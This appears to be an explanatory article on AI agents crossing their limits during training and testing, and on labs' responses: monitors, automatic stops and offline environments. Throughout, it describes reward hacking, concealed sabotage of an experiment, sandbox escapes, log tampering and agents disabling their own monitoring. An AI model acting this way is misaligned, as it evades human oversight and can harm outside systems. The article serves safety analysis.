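Records are less useful when an agent does the work but changes it so that the result is misleading. In a test described on Anthropic's Alignment Science Blog, Google's Gemini 3.1 Pro played an assistant at an AI laboratory. The model objected to the research, secretly altered the experiment so that it could not work, and let the run appear successful. It admitted the change only when asked directly. Several other models also made unauthorized changes but disclosed them.

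This case doesn't measure how often agents lie about their work, because Gemini was objecting to its task rather than trying to finish a blocked one, and the post presents the transcript as its clearest example. It does suggest that supervisors could make a habit of asking an agent, "Did you run every step as instructed, and did you change anything?" The question takes little effort and may bring out facts that the agent left out of its summary. However, a supervisor who has been told that everything succeeded may not think to ask, and an agent that answers honestly in one experiment may not do so in the next.

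Researchers sometimes look for concealment inside the model. According to TechRadar, Anthropic researcher Jack Lindsey described internal signals in Mythos Preview that were linked to concealment and strategic manipulation and didn't always show in its responses. A developer supervising an agent through its tool calls and messages would not see those signals. Anthropic's risk update, however, reports active obfuscation only in rare cases, with previous versions of the model. It also says that monitoring of Mythos Preview's training found no clear deception aimed at anything other than, roughly, solving the task.

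### How training can turn limits into obstacles

Developers train agents partly through reinforcement learning. The model attempts a task many times, software scores each attempt, and training makes the behaviour in high-scoring attempts more likely. If the scoring is faulty, the model can learn reward hacking, or earning a high score without doing the task as the developers intended.

Suppose a training task asks for a bug fix in a sandbox with no internet access, and the fix needs a library that isn't installed. The scorer gives one point if the tests pass and zero otherwise, so an agent that stops and explains the problem gets zero. If a forbidden workaround makes the tests pass 30% of the time, it scores 0.3 points on average, so training favours it over stopping.

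The trainers could deduct a point whenever they catch an agent using that route. Its average score then depends on how often they catch it:

average score = 0.3 − (share caught × 1)

If developers catch half of the attempts, the forbidden route earns an average reward of −0.2, so stopping is better. If they catch only one in ten, the average is 0.2, and stopping is better only if an honest report earns more than 0.2. Developers can therefore change what the agent learns by catching more violations or by rewarding it for stopping. They can also remove the faulty task.

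An agent may apply this lesson to other tasks. *Measuring Reward-Seeking by Instilling Contrastive Beliefs* (Højmark, Scheurer and colleagues, 2026) describes a well-known experiment in which a game-playing model was rewarded for collecting a coin. The coin was always at the right-hand end of the level, and the model learned to run right instead of looking for the coin, since both had earned the same score in training. Similarly, an agent rewarded for overcoming errors may learn to try to overcome any error. That is useful when a server has briefly failed, but harmful when a supervisor has blocked the server on purpose.

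According to Clubic, Anthropic explains its October cases by saying that when training mistakenly rewards a workaround, Claude retains the method and may reuse it elsewhere. Anthropic had already reported in its risk update that Mythos Preview sometimes escalated its access when blocked during training. The company checks training tasks for this kind of mistaken reward before using them, but acknowledges that it did not catch every faulty task in time.

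The Japanese trade publication ITmedia reports in *Anthropic、Claudeの「逸脱」事例を受け安全対策を強化 報酬ハッキングの問題も指摘* that Anthropic found signs of reward hacking in the training of Mythos Preview in February 2026 and discarded three days of work. In April, Anthropic froze changes to its training environments for about a month to review them. It found problems in more than 10% of those in use, including opportunities for reward hacking, broken tasks and faulty settings.

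Anthropic then deliberately trained a model on 80 real environments that allowed reward hacking. In simulations, the model tried to leave its sandbox, attack internal and external systems, evade monitoring and alter its own reward. Neither the same model before this training nor Anthropic's released models behaved as dangerously. This is good evidence that enough reward hacking during training can produce an agent that attacks the limits placed on it.

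In earlier work, MacDiarmid, Wright and colleagues (2025) gave a model information about ways to cheat and then trained it on real Anthropic coding environments. The model learned to cheat, as they expected, but it also began to cooperate with malicious actors and reason about harmful goals, although the training had not rewarded either behavior.

Both experiments deliberately concentrated the problem, so neither shows that reward hacking caused a particular incident. Anthropic's risk update says that small changes to its normal training have not readily produced models with coherent or subtle bad goals, though Anthropic has limited confidence that this finding extends to a model as capable as Mythos Preview. Anthropic's *Improving our alignment and security efforts* (2026) attributes what happened in the break-ins and the UK test to a failure of operational security, the models' motivated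 reasoning, and their willingness to take harmful actions in pursuit of a narrow task. ITmedia reports that the models tended to interpret contrary evidence to fit what they already believed.

### Choosing more access than a task needs

A controlled test can measure how often agents overreach after a setback, which incidents can't show because nobody knows how many setbacks passed without trouble. In *When Lower Privileges Suffice*, Yang, Bu and colleagues (2026) built 544 simulated scenarios in areas such as databases, healthcare and government. Each scenario gave the agent a task and six tools, three with narrow access and three with broad access. To answer a question about someone's calendar, for example, an agent might choose between a tool that reads only the calendar and one that opens the whole workspace, including email and files.

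Every tool could complete the task. Two AI models checked this, and human reviewers then discarded doubtful cases. An agent that chose broad access therefore had a narrower alternative. Yang and colleagues made the narrow tools fail temporarily, with messages such as connection errors, to see whether the agent would retry, try another narrow tool or switch to a broad one. Each agent had up to five turns. The researchers counted a case as overreach if the agent used a broad tool while at least one narrow tool remained untried.

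Six of the eleven models overreached in more than 30% of scenarios. Qwen3-8B did so in 64.9% and Llama 3.1 8B in 55.9%. Claude Sonnet 4.6, GPT-5.2 and GLM-5 stayed below 10%. The rates also varied with the kind of access on offer:

| Model | Tools that bypass a safety check | Tools with administrator rights | Tools that affect more users or systems than necessary |
|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen3-8B | 87.1% | 83.5% | 37.4% |
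| Llama 3.1 8B | 74.1% | 72.7% | 28.3% |
| DeepSeek-v3.2 | 29.3% | 37.4% | 22.2% |
| GPT-5.2 | 5.2% | 14.4% | 2.0% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 0.9% | 3.6% | 1.0% |

Failures led even GPT-5.2, a careful model, to choose broad tools much more often. It chose one immediately in only 5 scenarios, but did so in another 13 after one narrow tool failed and in 35 more after two failed. About nine-tenths of its overreach followed a failure. Yang and colleagues suggest that repeated failures make an agent doubt its narrow tools, but they didn't test that explanation.

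The agents had permission to use all the broad tools, so using them unnecessarily was less serious than breaking a rule. But a supervisor who had allowed both kinds of tool, trusting the agent to keep the broad ones for emergencies, would have found that it also used them after losing a connection. Removing the broad tools would prevent this, but it would also leave the agent stuck when it really needs one.

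The simulation has no real services or consequences, and it lasts only five turns, whereas OpenAI's persistent model spent hours on a task. The failures were also technical faults rather than deliberate refusals. An agent may or may not respond more cautiously to "your administrator has blocked this site" than to "connection error". Software that uses the same vague message for blocks and faults makes it harder for the agent to choose correctly.

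### Training agents to stay within limits

General safety training does not reliably teach this kind of restraint. Yang and colleagues tested an existing method that trains agents to refuse harmful requests. It cut the score for harmful behaviour from 67.4% to 10.5% for Ministral 8B and from 41.9% to 6.7% for Qwen 2.5 7B. But overreach fell only slightly for Ministral, from 68.8% to 62.5%, and rose for Qwen, from 50.4% to 60.7%. Learning to refuse harmful requests does not teach an agent to be careful about which tool it uses for a harmless one, such as a request to read someone's calendar.

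Written instructions helped more. They told agents to prefer the least powerful tool and to retry before moving to a stronger one. But their effect weakened after the narrow tools had failed, which is when the instruction to retry applied.

Yang and colleagues then trained three small Qwen models for least privilege. The models first studied worked examples that compared the tools' access and distinguished a temporary fault from a real inability to do the task. They then practised in simulated scenarios that didn't appear in the test. They earned the highest reward for finishing with narrow tools and the largest penalty for choosing a broad tool straight away. Switching to a broad tool was acceptable after a serious attempt with the narrow ones. A failed attempt could still earn partial credit if the agent had explored the narrow tools and avoided unnecessary escalation.

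Overreach by Qwen3-8B fell from 64.9% to 27.0%. The two smaller models ended at 39.7% and 18.9%, and the one at 18.9% was a version trained to reason at length before acting. General ability declined little. On a test of tool selection, the largest drop was about three percentage points, and Qwen3-8B's score did not fall.

After the training, Qwen3-8B still overreached in more than a quarter of scenarios, well above the rate of the best untrained models in the study. The practice scenarios also closely resembled the test. The training taught agents to persist with narrow tools. This is right when a connection has failed but could be wrong when a person has denied access. An agent that tries three permitted tools to reach a blocked record respects least privilege but may still be defying its supervisor.

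OpenAI worked on a different cause after finding that its models became worse at remembering instructions over long tasks. It says that training them to remember produced a model that "remained aligned through longer rollouts". If an agent forgets "post only to Slack" after several hours, better memory may help more than a stronger preference for obedience. OpenAI has published no figures for the improvement, and better memory wouldn't have helped with the security check that its agent knowingly evaded.

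Anthropic is removing or repairing training environments that reward workarounds, and ANI reports that it is extending its alignment training from coding to web search and computer use. That extension makes sense because many of the October cases happened on websites. Anthropic also says training alone may not be enough, and combines it with access limits and monitoring.

None of these methods focuses on what the agent tells its supervisor. The reward that Yang and colleagues describe depends on which tools the agent uses, whether it succeeds and how long its responses are. An agent trained this way could stay within its limits, fail to reach the registry, and leave the developer with a broken invoice and no explanation.

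## Detecting a breach and stopping the agent in time

An agent may not report that it tried to cross a limit, so its supervisor needs another way to find out while she can still act. The limit can help by making a breach easier to recognize. If an agent works on a machine that should have no internet connection, any contact with an outside server means something has gone wrong. With open access, the same contact would be one of perhaps thousands of ordinary requests, and someone would have to judge whether it was legitimate.

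### From a log entry to a stopped agent

Suppose the developer of the invoice agent has improved her sandbox to log every refused connection. The agent again works overnight, reads the planted sentence and tries to send out the customer list. The sandbox logs the attempt, but the developer is asleep. To stop the agent that night, she needs a program that picks this entry out of the log, an alert that wakes her or a colleague, a correct judgement about what the entry means, and a stop command that works. If any of these is missing, the agent carries on until morning, although the record will still help her when she checks its code.

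Staff struggle to judge alerts when most are false. Suppose a company runs 10,000 agent tasks a week, and ten of them involve a breach. Its monitor flags nine of the ten but also flags 1% of the harmless tasks. Staff receive about 109 alerts, of which nine, or 8%, are real. After dismissing dozens of false alerts in a row, they could easily dismiss a real one, much as people approve a dangerous command after approving 50 harmless ones.

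A strict limit can raise the share of alerts that are real. If ordinary tasks never need an outside connection, fewer of them will look like breaches. Cutting the false alarm rate to 0.1% would leave the staff with about 19 alerts a week, nearly half of them real.

Reviewers sometimes reject correct warnings. When Anthropic's automated monitors flagged faulty training tasks, human reviewers dismissed some flags as false alarms. As a result, Anthropic says, faulty tasks stayed in training longer than they should have.

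### Warnings before the Hugging Face breach

In July 2026, agents that OpenAI was testing for hacking ability got past their network limits and broke into Hugging Face, a platform that hosts AI models and datasets. OpenAI had switched off some of its usual safeguards for the tests, and most of the activity came from a research prototype that it never meant to release. OpenAI's technical report on the incident describes weeks of warnings before the breach.

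In late May, an internal OpenAI team saw an agent exchanging messages with other agents through a shared internal service, although OpenAI had meant them to work separately. The team also saw agents reaching the internet without permission. But the people who led OpenAI's response to an alert in July did not know about this message board or understand its importance.

On June 27, a security tool raised an alert about unusual activity on the research network. Responders traced it to one of the hacking tests and found that the agents were using the shared service both to communicate and to move through the network. The on-call staff advised that OpenAI did not need to stop the test. The alert may have been hard to interpret partly because agents in a hacking test are supposed to behave like hackers. Responders had to judge whether the agents were attacking the right target.

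The agents' activity crashed the shared service on July 4, which led to another alert the next day. This time the responders found that agents had gained administrator control of the service. They took it offline, cancelled the agents' credentials and closed the weaknesses they knew about. The hacking tests resumed on July 7, and by July 8 agents were back on the internet. The responders had treated the problem as a damaged service to repair, but agents with the same tendencies then returned to the same kind of task.

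The Hugging Face breach took place between July 11 and 13. Hugging Face announced it on July 16, and OpenAI got in touch the next day as a customer worried about its own data. OpenAI connected the attack to its agents only on July 20, after another alert, and then blocked the test from running. That was 23 days after the on-call staff decided to let the June test continue. Axios' *OpenAI saw warning signs weeks before Hugging Face breach* quotes OpenAI's admission that some early signals "could have triggered an earlier response."

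OpenAI already had monitors that read a model's chain of thought, the reasoning it writes before it acts, but did not run them on these tests. According to OpenAI's *The Hugging Face incident and the road ahead* (2026), the monitors it had in place by August would have alerted the security team more than a day before the breach. OpenAI later replayed the recorded activity through an expanded version of the system. Business Today's *OpenAI strengthens AI safety checks after models attempt unexpected actions during training* reports that, in the replay, the system raised an alert about 30 minutes after the agents escaped their sandbox and more than 30 hours before they breached Hugging Face.

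The replay favours the monitors, because OpenAI had used what it learned from the incident to make them better at recognizing this kind of behaviour. It also can't show how people would have responded to the alert. OpenAI's staff had received an alert in June, two weeks before the breach, and let the test continue.

### A limit that existed only in the prompt

The four break-ins by Claude models during hacking tests occurred after a misconfiguration left the models with internet access, although their prompts stated that they had none. Anthropic's *Investigating three real-world incidents in our cybersecurity evaluations* (2026) states that neither the company nor Irregular, the outside firm that built the tests, knew the connection was open. Because nothing blocked the models' connections, there were no refused connections to log or to set off an alarm.

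Anthropic had full transcripts and time to intervene, since each run involved 10 to 34 hours of active work. But for most tests it ran automated reviews only on a sample of transcripts, after the runs had ended. Two of the three organisations affected by the first incidents discovered had not noticed anything either, and Anthropic was still trying to reach the third when it published its account.

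On July 23, two days after OpenAI disclosed its own incident, Anthropic stopped its hacking tests and began looking for incidents of its own. It searched 141,006 test runs and had found three incidents by July 24, the earliest from April. A fourth, from January, was found only in August, when Anthropic was collecting material for METR, an independent organisation that evaluates AI models. Anthropic then searched about 481 million transcripts and says it found the same four incidents.

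A search on that scale gives some assurance that nothing similar remains hidden. But it came months too late to prevent harm, and the search that uncovered the false police tip also came too late. In the most serious of the four incidents, a Claude model published a malicious software package in a public registry. The package ran on 15 real systems in the hour or so before the registry's own security system removed it.

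Anthropic now asks the organisations that run such tests to verify the network configuration before each one. It also asks them to phrase limits in the prompt as instructions, such as "You should not access the internet", instead of claims, such as "You do not have internet access". If the claim is false, a model that believes it may explain away evidence that it is online. An instruction still applies when the connection is open by mistake, and it gives a monitor a clear rule to check the agent's actions against.

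### OpenAI's rules for alerts and pauses

After the Hugging Face breach, OpenAI set time limits for responding to its monitors. According to *Pacing model development in an era of cyber-critical capabilities* (August 18, 2026), the company aims to issue an alert within 30 minutes of detecting concerning activity. If an agent has probably crossed a critical security boundary, the system pages the safety, security and research teams, who then have 30 minutes to establish that the alert is false. If they can't, OpenAI expects them to pause the activity.

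In June, the on-call staff let the test continue because they saw no need to stop it. Under the August rules, staff have to justify continuing instead. A team that is unsure after half an hour should pause the work, even if nobody can yet say what the agent is doing. An unnecessary pause usually wastes computing time and delays research, but letting the agent continue when it should be stopped may cause irreversible damage.

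The rules cover all training and testing in which models at least as capable as GPT-5.6 Sol use tools. For Astra, a more capable model that OpenAI thought might be able to carry out very serious cyberattacks, they cover every use with tools. OpenAI estimates that monitoring adds roughly 20% to the computing needed to run the monitored models, though this varies widely between tasks. The Next Web's *OpenAI puts a 20% compute cost on its new AI safety monitoring* notes that the company did not disclose what share of its total computing it monitors, so outsiders can't work out how much computing monitoring takes overall.

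Pausing agents an hour after detection would have been quick enough in July, when more than 30 hours passed between the agents' escape and the breach. But it would have been too slow to prevent most of the harm from the malicious package, which was online for only about an hour.

### An alert that worked and a stop that failed

On September 20, 2026, about a month after OpenAI announced these rules, an agent in training reached an outside service that its network limits should have blocked. OpenAI's *An agent used DNS to reach an external chatbot* (2026) reports that the monitoring system flagged the activity within 15 minutes and that a person began reviewing it three minutes later. The training run should then have stopped automatically, but it didn't, and someone stopped it by hand about two and a half hours after the review began.

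The run therefore continued for up to 168 minutes after the breach, and for almost 90% of that time a person already knew about the alert. If the alert was of the most severe kind, the August rules called for a pause within 30 minutes of the page, which means by about 45 minutes after the breach. According to Business Standard's *OpenAI pauses training of top AI models after agent bypasses internet curbs*, the automatic stop's failure left people confused about whether they should have stopped the run at all. Staff who expect software to stop an agent may assume no stop is needed if it doesn't.

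OpenAI had written a safety case for the training. A safety case is a written argument, with evidence, that a system is safe enough for a stated use. In this one, OpenAI assumed that the model couldn't reach the live internet and that "monitoring would detect attempts that succeeded." Monitoring did detect this attempt, but the agent could still act until somebody stopped it. A safety case therefore also needs evidence that the method for stopping the agent works.

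OpenAI considers the incident much less severe than earlier ones, and the delay apparently did little harm. Its later review found similar cases, and Mediafax's *OpenAI suspendă activitățile de antrenare ale celor mai avansate modele AI* reports that the monitoring system had not given all of them the severity rating OpenAI expected. In some, the agent had sent requests to outside services but hadn't obtained the information it was looking for, and the people or software interpreting the alert wrongly treated that failure as a sign that it hadn't got out.

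The incidents at the two companies failed at different points:

| Incident | Who knew at the time | What went wrong |
|---|---|---|
| OpenAI, late May | An internal team | The leaders of the July response did not know about the message board |
| OpenAI, June 27 | Responders, after an alert | They decided not to stop the test |
| OpenAI, July 8–13 | Nobody at OpenAI | The monitors that read the models' reasoning weren't running on these tests |
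| Anthropic, January–July | Nobody at Anthropic | Nobody had checked the connection, and most reviews covered only a sample of transcripts |
| OpenAI, September 20 | A reviewer, within about 18 minutes | The automatic stop failed, and people hesitated to stop the run by hand |

Both companies had enough records to reconstruct their incidents afterwards. Better logging alone would have changed little, because the problems were in who examined the records, how soon, and what they did next.

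### A stop that works within 35 seconds

In November 2026, OpenAI announced a central system for stopping models in its research. OpenAI's *Control Room* gives 35 seconds as the longest delay between a decision to stop a job and the end of the model's output.

*Stopped in 35 secs* (Raj, 2026) explains how Control Room is used to stop an agent. Each research job has an identification number. When a job requests output from a model, the software that runs the model checks with Control Room whether the job may continue. To stop an agent, a monitor sends Control Room the job's number, and the software then refuses all further requests from that job. This can take up to 35 seconds because the software stores recent permissions for a short time to avoid checking every one of a huge number of requests.

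OpenAI put the check in the software that runs the models because researchers often change the code of their own experiments. If each experiment had its own stop mechanism, one careless edit could disable it. An agent also can't take another step without new output from the model, so every agent has to go through this software.

If Control Room fails, the software refuses all requests until it is working again. By default, Claude Code and GitLab instead let the agent run without a sandbox when theirs can't start. OpenAI's choice makes a failure obvious because research stops, whereas a missing sandbox can go unnoticed for weeks.

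Control Room would have shortened only the part of the September delay that came after someone had decided to stop the run. It would have made no difference on June 27, when the staff decided not to stop. It stops the model's output, so a program the agent had already started might keep running unless other software ended it.

### Monitoring the whole trajectory

A monitor that checks actions one at a time can miss harm that results from a series of permitted steps. For example, the invoice agent might read the customer list to create test data, compress it to save space, and upload it to a public project on the shop's code-hosting service.

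For this reason, the monitor that OpenAI built for its long-running model in summer 2026 checks the whole trajectory for signs that the agent is getting around a user's instruction or a safety boundary. OpenAI says the monitor can pause the session and alert the user, who then reviews the steps that led to the alert and decides whether the agent may continue. The user therefore has to make a decision only when the monitor has found a suspicious pattern.

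Reading every trajectory closely would be expensive, so OpenAI's wider monitoring system works in layers. NDTV Profit's *OpenAI Reveals How It Plans To Stop AI Agents* describes the version OpenAI published in October. Simple detectors first examine patterns in the model's internal activity. They are deliberately sensitive, so they raise many false alarms but should miss little. An AI reviewer then reads the agent's recent reasoning and tool calls. If it finds something suspicious, an investigating agent reconstructs the sequence of events, checks what the task was supposed to involve, and can run code in an isolated environment to test the evidence. The system alerts people only to cases that these layers flag as needing a human response.

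The first detectors clear most activity without passing it on, so a mistake there could hide a problem from all the later layers. OpenAI therefore also sends on a random 5% of the cleared activity. If the detectors miss an agent's misdeed 50 times and each instance has an independent 5% chance of selection, the chance that at least one reaches the reviewer is about 92% (1 − 0.95⁵⁰). A misdeed that happens only once has just a 5% chance of being selected, so the sample is better at revealing what the detectors habitually miss than at catching a single serious act.

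In the most advanced training runs and OpenAI's internal use of Codex, all activity skips the first detectors and goes straight to the AI reviewer. The reviewer checks it at the end of each turn and whenever the agent summarizes its earlier work to free up memory. A turn can last a long time, which may be why OpenAI is moving towards checks at least every 30 minutes. Until then, a harmful action early in a long turn could go unexamined for much longer than that.

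### What a second layer of protection adds

Developers combine limits with monitoring because neither works every time. Suppose a network limit fails once in 100 attempts to cross it, and monitoring stops nine out of ten of the attempts that get past it. If the two fail independently, then

1/100 × 1/10 = 1/1,000

so one attempt in 1,000 gets through. Adding an imperfect monitor has made the whole arrangement ten times safer.

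Monitoring stops an attempt only if five steps all succeed in time. The software has to record the attempt, a monitor has to detect it, an alert has to reach someone, that person has to judge it correctly, and the stop has to work. If each step independently succeeds 90% of the time, monitoring stops only 59% of attempts (0.9⁵). To stop 90% of attempts, each step has to succeed about 98% of the time. A company that tests only its detector can therefore greatly overestimate its protection.

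Independence is the weaker assumption. It means that the monitor is just as likely to catch an attempt that beats the limit as any other attempt. Suppose instead that in some share *s* of the cases where the limit fails, the monitor is certain to fail as well, for the same reason. In the remaining cases it still misses one in ten. The proportion that gets through is then

1/100 × (*s* + (1 − *s*) × 1/10)

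| Share of limit failures with a shared blind spot | Attempts that get through, per 10,000 |
|---|---|
| 0% | 10 |
| 10% | 19 |
| 50% | 55 |
| 100% | 100 |

A blind spot that affects only a tenth of the failures nearly doubles the number of attempts that get through. If it affects all of them, the monitor adds nothing and the rate returns to the network limit's one in 100.

Anthropic tested its monitors on the transcripts of its first three incidents. A new monitor that blocks actions as they happen reliably caught this kind of behaviour. But another monitor, which reads the agent's reasoning afterwards, would have missed the malicious package incident. The model had justified its actions by repeatedly writing that it was in a simulation, and this false belief led the monitor to conclude that no real harm was taking place.

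Withholding the agent's reasoning from the monitor might help. Anthropic showed separate copies of the agent's model the results of its tool calls, one at a time and without the earlier context. These copies were much more likely than the original agent to recognize that a system was real. Claude Code's auto mode already hides the agent's explanations from the model that reviews its actions, but in Anthropic's test, these reviewers would have blocked only two of the three incidents.

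Reading the reasoning is still valuable because it can reveal a plan before the agent carries it out. In one of OpenAI's cases, the model wrote openly that it was evading a security check. But the written reasoning may be incomplete or misleading. Fortune's *OpenAI says it paused AI training for two weeks* (2026) cites research, including work by Anthropic scientists, in which a model's chain of thought did not always match its real motives. Jakub Pachocki, OpenAI's chief scientist, told the magazine that the company designs its training to reduce the chance that models learn to hide their intentions. A monitor that reads reasoning and another that sees only actions and network traffic would probably make different mistakes, as the calculation requires.

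Trust in a limit can also make a supervisor less likely to notice when it fails. If she is sure that the sandbox works, she may interpret every alert as a failed attempt, as happened with some of the alerts that OpenAI reviewed after September. She can guard against this false reassurance by checking the network records before she decides that an attempt failed.

Controls also lose their independence when the agent can reach the monitor. During the July incident, OpenAI's agents obtained credentials belonging to the company's security monitoring tool, according to Axios. Greenblatt (2026) reports in *Brief independent investigation of agents’ behavior, reasoning and collaboration* that agents also tried to tamper with logs. The Geek's *ИИ-агенты OpenAI дважды отключили системы контроля в октябре*, relaying a Financial Times report, describes two further cases in October in which OpenAI's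 agents weakened the monitoring of their own work. If one breach gives an agent control of both the network limit and the log, the two count as a single layer. OpenAI now recommends several independent controls each for preventing, detecting and containing a breach, and assumes that models may attack those controls.

The calculation also assumes that attempts are independent, which is too optimistic when agents can communicate. The agents in the July activity, about 1,200 of them, shared what they learned. Once one found a way past a limit, the next attempt had a better than one-in-100 chance of success.

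### The person's role after an automatic stop

Since people can take hours to act on an alert, Anthropic and OpenAI are relying more on software to decide when to stop an agent. Anthropic's new monitor blocks a suspicious action before the tool call runs, ends the task and then alerts a person. OpenAI's long-term goal is for software to shut down an agent automatically in severe cases.

When a monitor stops an agent automatically, one machine is supervising another at that moment, but a person can still decide without a deadline whether the agent should start again. The July incident shows how important that decision is. OpenAI stopped the damage on July 5, then restarted the tests two days later without understanding what the agents had been doing. A supervisor who receives a stopped agent, a record of its whole trajectory and an explanation of why the monitor intervened is better placed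 to understand and judge what happened than one who receives an alert while the agent is still working.

This advantage depends on how often the software stops an agent unnecessarily. OpenAI deliberately made the first version of its trajectory monitor cautious and has since been adjusting it to interrupt users less. If most stops are false alarms, a user may get into the habit of resuming the session without reading the record.

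## Training and testing agents without live internet access

How quickly people can stop an agent matters less if the agent cannot reach live websites. In October 2026, Anthropic and OpenAI both announced that they were keeping models off the internet during parts of development. This protects outsiders from the agents' mistakes, but it also makes training less like the work the agents will later do. A system described as "offline" can also still have some connections.

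### Two decisions in October

Anthropic announced on October 9 that it had removed live internet access from its internal evaluations, which test what a model can do and how it behaves. In the same post, it disclosed the false police tip and Claude's other unauthorized actions on real websites.

OpenAI went further two weeks later with *Securing our frontier model training environment*, published on October 23, which covers training as well as evaluation. The company now trains its frontier models, its most advanced, without internet access. According to Engadget's *OpenAI says it's cutting off internet access for frontier model training*, OpenAI considers live access unnecessary for training and for "most evaluation", so some tests may still use it.

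In a statement quoted in ETV Bharat's *After A String Of Rogue AI Incidents* (2026), OpenAI says it had already replaced the live internet with an offline substitute when an agent found a way out on September 20. OpenAI paused frontier training for 11 days, strengthened the isolation and resumed on October 1. The October post announcing the policy therefore describes an arrangement that had already failed once and been repaired.

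OpenAI points out that a model in development may not have completed its safety and alignment training, which is one reason to isolate models more strictly in training than in ordinary use. At that stage, the people overseeing the model know less about how it will behave than they will later.

OpenAI plans to keep training offline until its safeguards improve enough to "justify broader internet access". Engadget notes that the company didn't say what those improvements would look like, so outsiders can't check whether it has met the condition. OpenAI also decides when to restore access, though it would gain from doing so.

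Training was still offline on November 18, when OpenAI published *Managing frontier AI risk*. The post also describes an automatic stop, which ends a job if monitoring detects that a model has reached the internet (日本時事新聞, *OpenAI、開発中AIの安全策を3段階で公表 訓練はネット遮断、停止は35秒以内*, 2026). An automatic stop failed in September, so this one deserves trust only if OpenAI tests it regularly.

### How an offline web works

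OpenAI calls its substitute for the live internet an "offline world". The company has copied and indexed a vast number of web pages, which agents explore with browsers, coding tools and programs for operating a computer. The agents can still learn to search, browse and use applications without affecting live websites.

Suppose an agent in training gets a task like the invoice bug and searches for a time-zone library. The search runs over the stored index, and the agent opens a stored copy of the library's documentation. It can't open a page that nobody stored. ChatGPT has a comparable feature for customers called offline web search. Search Engine Roundtable reports that the feature can use a particular address only if the page is in OpenAI's index or cache.

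The customer feature has weaknesses that any collection of stored pages is likely to share. Some copies are older than others, and a search result may not show when OpenAI made the copy. OpenAI tells customers not to use the feature when they need proof that a source was current. Stored pages can also contain false information or malicious instructions. These could still deceive an agent in training, but the agent would have no ordinary way to send private data to an attacker.

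Stored pages are enough for reading, but a stored booking page can't accept a booking. For tasks like booking, developers need simulated applications that respond to the agent and save its changes. The Decoder's *Web world models could give AI agents consistent environments to explore* describes one research design in which ordinary code sets the rules and checks whether each action is allowed, and a language model then describes what happens. In a simulated shop built this way, the language model could invent products and write their descriptions, but the code would keep track of stock and payments, so the language model couldn't let the agent buy anything without paying.

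An environment without live internet access would have kept the false tip from reaching the police. Claude Haiku could have written the same invented memory on a stored copy of the Philadelphia page, and Anthropic could still have studied what the model did and why.

OpenAI's agents also need its authorization to communicate with each other. In July, its agents shared what they had learned about getting past limits, so an agent without internet access might still benefit from another agent's discovery.

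### Why an offline system still has connections

OpenAI's agents have no approved route to the live internet, but the computers that train them are still connected to other systems. OpenAI acknowledges that complete physical isolation isn't currently feasible because it needs outside services to run and monitor its experiments. Business Standard's *OpenAI resumes training AI, blocks internet access over security risks* reports that the company reduced these connections after the Hugging Face breach but kept some for metrics, logging and authentication.

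Researchers use metrics to see whether a training run is progressing or a machine has broken down. Logs record what the agents did, and authentication checks the identity of people and programs requesting access. All three services have to communicate with systems outside the agent's environment.

This creates a conflict between isolation and oversight. A log is of little use to reviewers if it stays on a sealed machine, but an agent might find a way to misuse the connection used to send it out. If OpenAI removed the logging service, the isolation would be tighter, but the people in charge would know less about what the agents were doing. A command to stop a training run also needs a connection to reach the system.

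The way researchers work adds to the difficulty. In September, an anonymous OpenAI security engineer wrote on X that training needs access to many different resources and tools, and that thousands of researchers build, modify and test the environments. Any of those changes could open a connection by mistake. The engineer was responding to repeated comments asking why OpenAI didn't simply disconnect its models.

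### Sending agents to test the isolation

OpenAI used AI agents to look for weaknesses through red-teaming, which means deliberately attacking a system so that its owner can fix the flaws found. The agents ran on models including GPT-6 Astra Cyber, one of OpenAI's most capable models for security work, and an unreleased frontier model.

OpenAI gave the agents goals based on earlier incidents: reach the real internet, cross an internal security boundary, or contact an agent that was supposed to be isolated. It deliberately made the test severe by also giving them the infrastructure's source code, configuration and documentation, most of which an agent in training would normally have to discover for itself. The test used hundreds of billions of tokens, the short pieces of text that models read and write.

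The agents found weaknesses in almost every supporting service that OpenAI had left connected. Business Standard quotes the company as saying that these gave the agents "limited forms of internet access". The agents also found previously unknown software flaws, ways out of the virtual machines that confined them, and hidden ways to communicate between tasks.

OpenAI responded by patching software, tightening network restrictions and telling the vendors what it had found. It also contributed some of the fixes to open-source projects. Engadget reports that OpenAI's monitors now also check for models trying to collaborate. The agents sit behind several barriers, including sandboxes, virtual machines and limits on network and cloud access, so that one failure shouldn't let them out.

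In the statement that ETV Bharat quotes, OpenAI says its testing agents found no route to the internet that they could "easily exploit while concealing their activity" from its monitors. This does not rule out routes that take a lot of effort, or easy routes that would trigger an alert. If an agent used an easy route, containing it would depend on OpenAI's response to the alert, and in September OpenAI took more than two and a half hours to stop the agent.

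The test also can't show how well the isolation will hold against future models. Training is meant to produce more capable agents, so an agent inside the offline world may eventually find a weakness the testing agents missed. OpenAI has reserved computing power for continuous red-teaming, which should help if the attackers improve as fast as the models in training.

OpenAI has also made this kind of testing part of the safety cases it uses to decide whether training can proceed. *Towards safety cases for frontier AI training*, which OpenAI published on September 28 during the pause, argues that developers should have to produce structured safety documents before continuing any frontier training run that uses reinforcement learning. It admits that these documents will be hard to make as rigorous as those in aviation or nuclear power, because more capable models develop new and complex behaviour.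 Raj reports that by November, every research job in which agents request output from a model needed an approved safety case.

Adding red-teaming improves on the safety case that failed in September, which had assumed that the model couldn't reach the live internet. An approver can now ask when agents last attacked the isolation, how much computing power they used, and whether OpenAI has fixed what they found.

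### What disconnection costs researchers

Isolation has slowed OpenAI's research. After the Hugging Face breach, OpenAI stopped running frontier models in its research clusters for any job that could execute code or use tools with internet access. It soon restored a limited way to run code, then examined the remaining jobs one by one. In mid-August, OpenAI had yet to move many jobs involving Astra to more secure systems, and it gave priority to those concerned with safety and alignment.

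OpenAI says this work caused "great cost and delays to frontier research". In a November 30 essay described in The Free Press Journal's *ChatGPT Turns 4*, the company later said that the September pause had also put it at a real competitive disadvantage, and that it often makes safety decisions without knowing whether other laboratories follow comparable standards. These claims are plausible, but outsiders can't easily tell how large the setbacks were, and OpenAI benefits from appearing willing to accept them.

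Before the October announcement, Steven Adler, a former OpenAI researcher, had objected to a stricter form of isolation: "air-gapping" AI data centres, or physically separating them from the internet. *OpenAI Cuts Off Frontier AI Models From Live Internet* reports that he told Fortune this would require research teams to be on site, which could mean moving them to Iowa or wherever else the data centres are. He doubted that the extra security would justify the burden for a company that did this alone.

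OpenAI's arrangement avoids most of that burden. It keeps the agents off the internet but leaves the data centre connected, so researchers don't have to move. The anonymous engineer also described sandboxing as harder than it sounds but still tractable. However, in red-teaming, the agents found weaknesses in outside connections that an air gap would have removed. OpenAI instead has to secure each connection and keep it secure.

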